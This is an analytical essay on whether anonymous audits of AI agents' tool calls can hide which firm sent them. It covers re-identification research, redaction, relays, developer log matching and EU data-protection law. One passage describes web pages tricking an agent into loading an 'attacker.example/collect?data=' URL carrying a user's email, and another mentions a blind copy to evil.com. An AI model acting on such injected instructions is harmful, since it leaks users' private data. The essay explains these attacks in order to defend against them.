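Search queries can reveal even more than a list of sites. Gurung and colleagues gave a language model only the web searches that a company's agent had made. When a small model, Qwen3-4B, ran the agent, the language model recovered at least part of a private fact about the company in 34.0% of the tasks. In one example, the agent searches twice for a shop's online growth in 2020, then searches for something else involving the figure 15%. None of the searches states the growth rate, but together they suggest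 it was 15%. Similar searches by the law firm's agent would expose the client's secrets as well as the firm's identity.

### From chats and interviews to tool calls

None of these experiments tested whether companies can be identified from their agents' real tool-call logs, and no such published test has been found. The closest experiment, by Gurung and colleagues, used invented company documents and looked for business facts rather than the sender's identity. The others involved individual people. Applying the results to the law firm therefore requires inference, and some of the differences would make the firm easier to identify while others would make it harder.

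Some differences between agents' requests and people's chats make a firm harder to identify. People write their own chats, but a model writes an agent's searches, so the requests of two firms that use the same model may read alike. A single request also contains less text than a conversation, and Pham and colleagues generally found longer conversations easier to match. A large firm works for many clients at once, so its requests have no single subject.

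But an audit log also contains details that the benchmark left out. Before testing the programmers' sessions, Pham and colleagues removed all file paths, URLs, account names and project names. An auditor needs the URLs to judge a page fetch, and often needs the paths to judge what an agent does with a file. A log that keeps them may therefore reveal more than the benchmark results suggest, though nobody has measured how much. The auditor also has only 200 firms to choose from, compared with thousands of people in the attack on general chats.

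### The law firm's four requests again

The document link and the client email both contain the firm's name, so the auditor can identify the firm without embeddings or web searches. Removing the signature from the email would still leave Northgate's address, which may identify the firm almost as well as its name does.

The docket fetch narrows the possible customers to the six firms on the case. Deleting names can't fix this, because the choice of page reveals the connection to the case. *AgentTell* (2026) describes the same problem with agents that browse for a user. In its running example, the user tells the agent not to give any website their personal details. The agent reads the user's job title in a staff directory, then picks material relevant to that job on another site, whose operator can infer the job from the choice.

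The merger search comes closest to revealing nothing about its sender. Suppose 30 of the 200 firms have some reason to make it. Alone, it would leave the auditor with 30 candidates. If the auditor knows that the docket fetch came from the same sender, however, it can look for firms on both lists. Each of the other five firms on the case has about a 15% chance of being among the 30, so on average fewer than one of them remains. (This treats the two lists as independent. Firms on a Northgate case are probably more interested in its merger than others, so a few more might remain.)

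Over a full day, at least one of the firm's requests will almost certainly contain its name. If each of its 500 requests has a 1% chance of containing the name, the chance that none does is less than 1%. The relay therefore can't keep the auditor from learning that the firm is a customer. It can still keep the auditor from attributing to the firm the roughly 495 requests that don't name it, provided that their content doesn't link them.

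This kind of identification is also a poor substitute for a name that an authority can reveal, because it exposes honest firms that sign their emails, but the invoice fraudster can avoid it by telling an agent to write under another company's name.

### Changing the request itself

The firm could have its agent send less identifying information. The auditor would lose nothing, because it would still see exactly what the agent sends.

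Warning the agent to protect private information is the simplest way to reduce leaks, but it isn't very effective. When Gurung and colleagues added a privacy warning to the small model's instructions, the share of tasks that leaked private facts fell only from 34.0% to 25.5%, mainly because the agent searched the web less. Training worked better. They rewarded the model for finding the right documents and penalised searches that revealed private facts, either alone or together with earlier ones. The share of tasks with leaks fell to 6.5%, and the model solved 58.1% of the tasks, up from 48.7% before training. The share of searches containing the company's name fell from 42.9% to 16.8%.

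Removing every name from the trained model's searches reduced leaks to 1.1%, but the model then solved only 52.6% of the tasks. When Gurung and colleagues trained the model only to solve tasks, without the privacy penalty, leaks rose to 51.8%, partly because the model searched more. A firm that buys a more capable agent may therefore reveal more.

Software can also check each outgoing request. *ToolMinimize* (2026) proposes rewriting a tool call's arguments to remove private information that the tool doesn't need, and *ArguShield* (2026) checks whether each value is necessary for the task and the recipient before the agent releases it. These methods could remove a client's name from a search that doesn't need it, but like the smart-home sanitizer, they can't remove details that a request depends on.

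The agent could also reveal less to an observer by visiting fewer sites. Jeong and colleagues found that reports based on only 10% of the usual domains scored about as well as reports based on all of them (8.54 compared with 8.55).

### What redaction costs the auditor

The firm could instead leave the request alone and change only the auditor's copy, but the auditor would then judge something different from what the agent sends. Four remedies would change the record of the client email as follows.

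| Remedy | What the auditor receives | What can still identify the firm | What the auditor loses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Strip the arguments | `send_email` | An unusual tool name | The recipient and the text |
| Send only domains | `send_email`; to: `northgate.example` | The client's domain | The person addressed and the text |
| Replace names | `send_email`; to: `ADDRESS-1`; body: `Our note is attached. PERSON-1, ORG-1` | The subject and any unusual details | Whether the address is the right one |
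| Batch customers | The full record, hours later, mixed with other firms' | Everything in the text | The chance to stop the email |

Stripping the arguments protects the firm best, but it leaves the auditor with very little to check. For example, the auditor wouldn't see the blind copy to evil.com in Microsoft's sample record. It could still notice an agent using a tool that its task doesn't require, if the firm told it which tools to expect. A firm that gave its tools unusual names would still have to rename them, because the names could identify it.

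With only domains, the auditor could check requests against a list of known dangerous sites, but it couldn't tell a harmless page from a fake login page on the same hosting service. The document link would also still show `docs.firm.example`. The results from Jeong and colleagues suggest that domains hide the specific subject of a task better than its purpose. Sending only `courts.example` works well for the docket fetch, because every law firm opens court websites. The auditor loses little useful information, since a court's docket pages are all about equally safe.

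Replacing names is the usual way to anonymise text, and Wen and Li measured how well it works. They took 143 of their interviews that at least one model had already identified, and tested whether 12 combinations of models and settings could still identify them after different treatments.

| Treatment | Average share identified | Characters changed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 75.1% | None |
| Mask the names | 62.0% | 0.42% |
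| Mask the names and paraphrase | 45.9% | 1.50% |
| Redact passages that a model trained on earlier attacks flags as risky | 35.1% | 2.64% |
| Replace true details with false ones | 34.2% | 0.85% |

After names were removed, at least one attacker could still identify 85.3% of the people. A job description, a project and a span of years can be enough to identify someone. False details prevented identification best on average, but some models treated the contradictions as transcription errors and still named the right person.

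Substituting false details also doesn't work for most of an audit record. If the firm's software replaces the docket page's URL or an email address with another, the auditor judges the wrong page or address. Redacting risky passages can remove evidence the auditor needs, because a detail that identifies the firm may also show whether the request is safe. *LLM Anonymization Against Agentic Re-Identification* (2026) proposes finding such details and rewriting them so that the text stays useful, but its tests used interviews, where a vaguer description often does no harm.

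Placeholders can preserve some of what the auditor needs if the software uses them consistently within a task. Suppose the lawyer's instruction mentions `ADDRESS-1`, and the agent then tries to send the email to `ADDRESS-1` with a blind copy to `ADDRESS-2`. The auditor can see that the lawyer never mentioned the second address and block the email without knowing what either address is. But it couldn't check `ADDRESS-2` against a list of known criminals, and it would have to trust the firm's software to give nearly identical addresses different placeholders. The software should also assign new placeholders for every task, because reused ones would link the firm's requests to each other, as a pseudonym would.

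The auditor could promise to instruct its own model not to identify anyone. When Wen and Li gave their attackers such an instruction, the average share identified fell from 75.1% to 21.6%, a larger drop than any change to the text produced. But in 37% of the cases where a model withheld the name, it had found the name in its searches, so the auditor's staff could read it in the search logs. The firm would also have to trust the auditor to keep the instruction in place.

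Batching hides the time and order of requests but not their content. In one example from Pham and colleagues, the attack linked two WildChat conversations by the same user, five months apart, among more than 40,000 candidates. Batching would keep the auditor from using the two-second gap between the docket fetch and the merger search to connect them. It would also hide the order of the steps in the invoice fraud, and the auditor would see Friday's email too late to stop it. Gurung and colleagues didn't test a mix of searches from several users, so it isn't clear how much harder mixing would make it to piece together a company's secrets.

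The firm could add decoys to the batch. In tests by Jeong and colleagues, one decoy task for every real one lowered the observer's score for purpose from 0.77 to 0.61, and five for every real one lowered it only to 0.57. The firm would have to pay for the decoys and their audits, and the auditor could no longer tell how often real agents break the rules.

The four requests differ so much that using one remedy for all of them would be wasteful. The firm's software could send the merger search in full through a relay, reduce the docket fetch to its domain, and check the document link locally against a list of the firm's own servers. The client email would go to an auditor in sealed hardware or stay at the firm. The relay would then carry only the requests it can protect, but the software would have to recognise the ones it can't. A filter that looks only for names would let the docket fetch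 through unchanged.

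## What happens when the auditor is also the developer

If the developer also sells the audit, it can identify the law firm by looking up each anonymous record in its own logs. Its model wrote the tool calls, so its servers have the same text next to the account that paid for it. This works even if the records contain no signature and the pages requested don't point to the firm.

The auditor is likely to also be the developer, because developers already check their customers' traffic for abuse. This undermines the case for a relay, which depends on the auditor having no other way to learn who sent a request.

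### Looking up the same request

Suppose the developer's models write 50 million tool calls a day, spread evenly, and the firm sends its audit records through an independent relay with a fresh token for each. The docket fetch might go like this (all the figures are invented):

1. At 14:02:05, the model writes a `fetch_url` call with the docket page's address. The developer's server logs the text, the time and the firm's account.
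2. The firm's software receives the call, removes the account details, encrypts a record for the developer's audit gateway and sends it through the relay.
3. At 14:02:06, the gateway decrypts the record and finds the tool name and the URL, but no name.
4. The developer searches its log for the same URL in the two seconds before the record arrived.

Fifty million calls a day is about 579 per second, so the two-second window contains about 1,160. If one call in a million uses this URL, the expected number of other matches is

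1,160 × 1/1,000,000 ≈ 0.001.

The developer will almost always find a single match, the firm's account. The separation fails because the developer has another copy of the request that never went through the relay. The encryption and the blind signature are still intact, and the relay's operator hasn't colluded with anyone.

The firm could hold its records back until more traffic accumulates. In an hour there are about 2.1 million calls, and about two others would use the same URL. A developer that picked one of the matching calls at random would still be right about 42% of the time. (If the number of other matches follows a Poisson distribution with mean *λ* = 2.08, the average chance of a correct guess is (1 − *e*<sup>−*λ*</sup>)/*λ*.) An hour's delay also rules out a live check. A URL with a unique parameter, such as `courts.example/docket/26-0417?session=8f3a91`, stays unique however long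 the firm waits, and so does the text of the client email.

Sending less text helps if the firm also waits before sending it. Suppose the record contains only `courts.example`, and one call in 10,000 goes to that domain. Two seconds of the developer's logs would contain about 0.12 other matching calls, but an hour would contain about 208. Replacing names with placeholders helps much less, because the developer can make the same replacements in its own logs and compare the results.

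The developer wouldn't even have to keep the text. A 32-byte hash and an 8-byte account number for each call would take up 2 gigabytes a day, which fits easily on a laptop.

The harm is smaller than it may seem, though, because the developer knew which page the firm's agent wanted to open before the audit began. Luo and colleagues treat anything the auditor learns through other channels as prior knowledge, which SealCall isn't designed to protect. A match gives the developer the verdict and any context that the firm added only for the audit, such as a list of approved recipients. An anonymous record can still protect the firm from people who see the audit data but not the model's logs, such as a contractor or a thief.

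A firm that runs the model on the developer's servers has already disclosed its requests to the developer, so no audit protocol can hide them.

### Who runs the model and the tools

How much each method still protects depends mainly on where the model runs.

| Arrangement | Relay | Anonymous token | Encrypted scoring | Auditor in a TEE |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Developer runs the model and the tools | Hides nothing, because the request starts on the developer's servers | Hides nothing unless the firm also pays for the model anonymously | Hides nothing about the request, which the developer carries out in plain text | Keeps audit staff from reading the record, but the developer has another copy |
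| Developer runs the model, firm runs the tools | Hides the firm's address, but the text leads to its account | Hides the payment, but the text leads to the account | Hides the verdict and any context added for the audit | Hides the added context from staff, but not the tool call |
| Firm runs an open-weight model | Hides the firm, unless the text identifies it | Hides which firm paid | Hides the text and the verdict | Hides the text from the developer's staff |
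| Firm runs an open-weight model, developer owns the relay | Hides nothing | Hides the payment, but the address identifies the firm | Hides the text and the verdict, but not the sender | Hides the text, but not the sender |

When the developer also runs the tools, the customer may have no request to send to an auditor, and the developer may keep a full history. According to Anthropic's *API and data retention*, Anthropic keeps transcripts from Claude Managed Agents, a service for running agents, until the customer deletes them, unless the customer hosts the agents itself.

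If the firm runs its own tools, encrypted scoring would prevent the developer from comparing texts, but the developer could still compare times. The 200 firms together make 100,000 requests a day, or about 2.3 every two seconds, and the developer probably knows which accounts buy audits because it sold them the tokens. When an encrypted record arrives, only two or three other requests would typically match its timing.

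SealCall's keys make this worse because they let the developer see which records share a sender. Any other firm has about a 1.2% chance of making a request in a given two-second window, so the expected number of other firms that fit two records with the same key is 199 × 0.012<sup>2</sup>, or about 0.03. Waiting an hour works much better for encrypted records than for readable ones, because nearly every firm makes some request in any given hour and the developer has no text to tell them apart.

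If the firm runs an open-weight model on its own computers, the developer receives no prompts or tool calls and has nothing to match. It is then in the same position as an outside auditor, and the relay works as intended, although the document link still contains the firm's domain name. The firm has to pay for the hardware and can't use models that developers offer only as a service. It could instead rent an open-weight model from a hosting company, which would have both the text and the account. The developer would need that company's help to find a match.

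Who owns the relay matters most when the firm runs the model itself. A developer that owns the relay can see both the firm's address and the decrypted record. If the developer only pays for the relay, the firm has to trust the relay's operator to resist pressure from the developer, as WhatsApp's users trust Fastly to resist pressure from WhatsApp. When the developer runs the model, an independent relay adds little privacy, because the developer can identify the firm without the relay's records.

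The firm could also use the developer's model anonymously, with a proxy and tickets like Open Anonymity's. A match would then lead to an unnamed session instead of an account. But the session would contain the whole Northgate task, including the document link. Pham and colleagues also showed that a provider with users' earlier named chats can re-identify some anonymous ones. A developer that verifies its customers might not allow this kind of access.

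### A link check that the developer runs itself

OpenAI already checks one kind of external request against data that it collected without looking at its users. Its *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes a defence against web pages that trick an agent into loading an address containing private information, such as `attacker.example/collect?data=` followed by the user's email address. The attacker then reads the information in the site's logs. The user may notice nothing, because the agent can make the request just by loading an image.

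OpenAI checks whether the exact URL an agent requests is in an index of public URLs. A crawler builds this index much as a search engine does, without access to conversations or accounts. If the URL is in the index, the agent can load it automatically. Otherwise, OpenAI either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user, who decides whether to open the link. OpenAI also considered a list of trusted sites but found it inadequate, because many sites redirect visitors elsewhere and a strict list would cause frequent false alarms.

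The check works only if the index is independent of users. If OpenAI added addresses from conversations, a URL containing one user's secret could enter the index and pass as public. The lookup still isn't anonymous, because OpenAI both serves the user and makes the lookup, so it could know who wanted which page.

OpenAI never claimed to hide this from itself. The check is meant to stop an agent from quietly leaking a user's data to a website through the URL. OpenAI says the check doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions. The docket page is public, so it would presumably pass. The document link would probably trigger a warning, because a crawler shouldn't be able to find a confidential memo.

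An outside auditor could use the same idea with more privacy. If the firm ran its own model, it could check URLs against such an index through a relay with private information retrieval, and the auditor would learn neither who sent the URL nor what it was. This would take more resources than the phishing lookups in Kim's tests, because an index of the public web is much larger than a list of phishing sites. Hiding the URL this way would be pointless inside ChatGPT, because OpenAI already has it.

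### Promising not to keep the text

To match an audit record with last week's traffic, the developer needs a log of that traffic. By default, OpenAI keeps logs of API use, which may contain prompts and responses, for up to 30 days to monitor for abuse. It keeps them longer if the law requires it or if it needs them to protect someone from harm. In *Offering Zero Data Retention for frontier models* (2026), OpenAI promises eligible customers that it will not retain prompts or responses after processing a request.

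Zero data retention works best with a delayed audit, because a developer that keeps its promise has nothing to compare with an audit record that arrives the next day. It helps less with a live check, because it restricts what the developer stores but not what it compares while handling a request. After the agent fetches the docket page, the firm's software typically sends the page back to the model with the conversation so far, including the original tool call. The same text is then on the developer's servers again within seconds of the audit.

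The promise also has exceptions. Even under its zero-retention agreements, Anthropic keeps the results of its safety classifiers, which are programs that sort text by risk. It uses these results to enforce its rules, so it presumably stores them with the customer's account. If it also stores the time of each result, it could use timing to match audit records to customers, even without the text.

If Anthropic's systems flag a session for breaking its rules, Anthropic may keep the inputs and outputs for up to two years, even for a customer with zero data retention. The text of an agent's most suspicious requests is therefore the most likely to remain available for matching. Anthropic's *API and data retention* also excludes data that outside websites and tools process from zero data retention, so the court's server can keep its own record of the docket fetch.

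The exceptions also depend on the model, so for now a firm has to check the terms for each one it uses. In June 2026, Anthropic began requiring data retention for its Mythos-class models, including for organisations that had zero data retention. Its documentation sets the period at 30 days unless Anthropic expressly authorises an exception. Businesses with sensitive data objected. Willing (2026), in *Anthropic Drops Data Retention Requirement for Mythos and Fable 5.1*, reports that a new system, Enterprise Frontier Safeguards, should eventually give them the same privacy as zero data retention.

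Developers keep text partly to detect dangers that appear only across several requests, like the invoice fraud. In August 2026, OpenAI previewed Private Safety Processing, which is meant to strengthen safeguards across interactions while preserving zero data retention. If it works, developers will have less reason to keep readable logs.

A customer can't get zero data retention anonymously, because both companies require approval first. The firm also can't confirm from outside that the developer has deleted anything.

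### Keeping two teams apart

The developer could instead keep both sets of records and restrict who sees them. One team would handle accounts and model logs, and another would receive the audit records without names. Luo and colleagues allow for one company running both the agent and the audit service, but they say the protection then depends on who can actually access the data and the keys. Dividing the work between teams would not hide customers' identities if both teams could query the same database.

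Suppose an employee on the audit team sees the merger search and wants to know which firm is working for Northgate. If the team can't access the model logs, the employee needs a colleague's help or has to break in. If the company records every search of those logs, it could identify the colleague afterwards. These measures help protect against a curious or corrupt employee, and a company can introduce them without new cryptography.

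But the same management controls both teams and can change their access. A court can order the company to produce both sets of records, and an attacker who gains control of the company's central systems may get both. The developer could also edit or ignore the access log. An outside body would need its own copy of the log and the power to ask why someone had searched for the firm's request. Even then, it would find out about a match only after someone had made it.

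### Summaries instead of conversations

Anthropic's Clio, now called Anthropic Insights, lets staff study how people use Claude without reading their conversations. Tamkin, McCain and colleagues (2024), in *Clio*, describe how it reduces the private information at each step. Applied to the law firm's requests, the process would look like this:

1. A model summarises each conversation and leaves out private details. The Northgate task might become "research a pending merger".
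2. The system groups similar summaries and discards any group with too few accounts or conversations.
3. A model describes each remaining group, again without private details.
4. Another model reads the descriptions and removes any that still contain private information.

Tamkin and colleagues tested 5,000 conversations and found private information in about 10% of the originals, about 1.5% of the summaries and none of the group descriptions. A model made these judgements, but it had been right 98% of the time on a separate set of test examples. Private information included details that identify a small organisation, so the test covers firms as well as people.

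Anthropic promises that employees who use Clio for general research get no access to raw conversations. But the original text is still on Anthropic's servers, so Clio protects the law firm from the people who read the descriptions, not from Anthropic as a company.

Clio's privacy steps also make it a poor auditing tool. A group must include several accounts, so Clio would discard the invoice fraud if only one customer attempted it. Tamkin and colleagues acknowledge that Clio isn't useful for rare events such as a single case of extreme misuse.

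When Anthropic uses Clio for safety, it therefore drops the minimum group sizes and the final privacy check, and lets authorised staff trace the results back to accounts. This helped it find a network of automated accounts that were producing spam for search engines, although no single conversation broke the rules. These safety runs include some traffic from businesses that use Anthropic's API, but exclude certain trusted organisations with zero-retention agreements. This matters for an audit on behalf of the public because a developer with a working system for anonymous summaries still chose to make accounts identifiable when it had to stop someone.

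Outsiders might be able to identify people from the published summaries. Anthropic gave privacy researchers at Imperial College London two weeks to try this with the results of three studies. According to Anthropic's *Appendix to “Enabling independent research on how people use Claude”* (2026), the researchers identified no users but linked one group to a popular open-source project. The test assumed an attacker outside the company and didn't cover Anthropic's own use of the system. In *CLIOPATRA*, Annamalai, De Cristofaro and Kairouz (2026) attacked a local copy of Clio and recovered private facts from invented medical chats in up to 65% of cases. Anthropic considers such an attack possible but far too difficult for the reward, while Annamalai and colleagues doubt that the Imperial College test rules it out.

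### Sealing the model as well as the log

Summaries and separate teams leave readable text on the developer's servers. The auditor-in-a-box design encrypts the stored logs, but the model has to process each prompt unencrypted first. On an ordinary server, the developer can copy the text or save a hash of it at that point, and the encrypted log won't show that it did.

To prevent this, the developer would have to run the model inside sealed hardware too. The law firm's software would encrypt the prompt so that only the attested program running the model could read it. That program would encrypt the tool call before returning it, and would write a log that only the auditor's program could read. The developer would still know that the firm's account had used the model at 14:02:05 and how much data it had sent, but would have no text to search.

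The firm would have to check the program that serves the model as carefully as it checks the auditor's program. One added line of code that saved a hash of every tool call would let the developer match requests to customers again. The developer could keep the model's weights secret, but it would have to let the firm or a trusted expert inspect the code around them. It would also have to move its own abuse checks inside the hardware or give them up.

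In live audits, timing would still give the developer a clue about which firm deployed the agent. With about 2.3 other requests in each two-second window, the developer could guess the right firm about 39% of the time without reading any prompts. If audit staff could read the records, they could then attribute some of them to the firm. If the auditor's program were sealed as well, the developer would learn only that the firm had probably had something audited. Holding the records for an hour would remove most of this clue, but only for audits that can wait.

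There is no known published test of this combination. WhatsApp's system shows that a large company can run a model in sealed hardware behind a relay, but that system is meant to answer users, not to audit agents. The combined design relies on the hardware for both the model and the audit, so an attack that forged attestations could expose the firm through either one.

### An auditor from another company

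The simplest fix is for the firm to buy its audits from someone other than the developer. An independent auditor receives the docket record through the relay but doesn't have the developer's traffic log, while the developer has the log but doesn't receive the record. Matching the two would again require them to collude by sharing data. The auditor could be a rival developer, as long as the firm doesn't use the rival's model for the same task.

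The auditor can lose its independence in ways the firm may not notice. If the auditor judges each request with a language model rented from the same developer, it sends the text of the docket record back to the developer that wrote it. The developer sees the auditor's account instead of the firm's, but it can still search for the URL. The contract should specify which models the auditor uses, who runs them, and what happens to old records if the developer buys the auditor.

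Even with an independent auditor, the developer can still observe the firm, because it has the firm's prompts and may run its own abuse checks on them. The firm gets a second opinion without revealing its name to the auditor.

An auditor working for the public may have to get its records from the developer instead of the customer. A recent pilot shows how much the developer then controls. Anthropic let groups at Stanford, Oxford and METR ask their own questions about roughly 250,000 conversations each. The researchers were free to publish unwelcome findings, and Anthropic could review their work only for user privacy, dangerous information, its own confidential information and accuracy.

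But the researchers never saw a conversation. Anthropic drew the samples, ran the analysis on its own servers and decided which results to release. It redacted or removed between 1.8% and 3.3% of the groups in each study, and it withdrew the results of one Oxford question because it suspected the wording had produced misleading descriptions. The researchers couldn't have checked this against the original text. Anthropic also found the process slow and costly. The pilot excluded its business customers, so it provides no direct evidence about firms like the one in the example.

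The pilot is good evidence that outsiders can choose the questions and publish inconvenient answers without learning who the users are. It is weaker evidence that they could catch a developer or customer who wanted to hide something. To do that, they would need records from another source, such as the outside services that receive the agents' requests.

### When a record without a name is still personal data

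European data protection law treats these arrangements differently, as a dispute about a failed Spanish bank shows. *European Data Protection Supervisor v Single Resolution Board*, decided by the Court of Justice of the European Union in 2025, concerned comments from the bank's former shareholders and creditors. The Single Resolution Board, an EU agency that deals with failing banks, sent 1,104 of the comments to the consulting company Deloitte. Each carried a random code instead of a name, and only the Board could link the codes to the commenters. Some commenters complained that the Board hadn't told them about Deloitte.

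The Board had also prevented its staff who processed the comments from seeing the authors' identities or the information that linked the codes to them. The Court nevertheless held that the comments remained personal data for the Board, because the Board as an organisation had the means to identify the authors. A developer that keeps its audit team away from its account records is in a similar position.

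Deloitte's position could be different. The Court held that data without names may not be personal for a recipient that cannot undo the measures that hide the names, provided those measures also prevent it from identifying people in other ways, such as by cross-checking with other data. An independent auditor behind a relay might meet both conditions for many requests. It would fail them for the client email because A. Reyes signed it.

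A developer that audits its own customers' requests would almost certainly fail the cross-checking condition, because searching two seconds of its log is a form of cross-checking. The Court disregards a method of identification if the law prohibits it or if it would take a disproportionate amount of time, cost and labour, and this search would take very little of each. It is less clear whether a contract that forbids the search would count as a legal prohibition. An independent auditor's position could also change, because identifiability under the rules depends partly on available technology, and language models have made it easier to identify people from text.

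Hiding the names doesn't remove the duty to tell people where their data goes. In its press release, *Judgment of the Court in Case C-413/23 P* (2025), the Court explains that this duty depends on what the organisation collecting the data knows at the time, not on what the recipient can work out later. The ruling interprets the regulation for EU institutions, but the Court reads that regulation in line with the general rules for companies. A law firm in the EU might therefore have to tell its lawyers about the auditor even if the auditor could never identify them. The bank case is still unresolved because the Court sent it back to the lower court.

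These rules protect only individual people, which is their main limit for an anonymous audit. They cover A. Reyes and the lawyer who typed the task, but not The Firm LLP. If an auditor worked out that the firm was interested in Northgate's merger but learned nothing about any individual, the firm would have to rely on its contract and on other laws, such as trade secret law. The distinction is harder to draw for a lawyer who practises alone, because identifying the practice also identifies the person.
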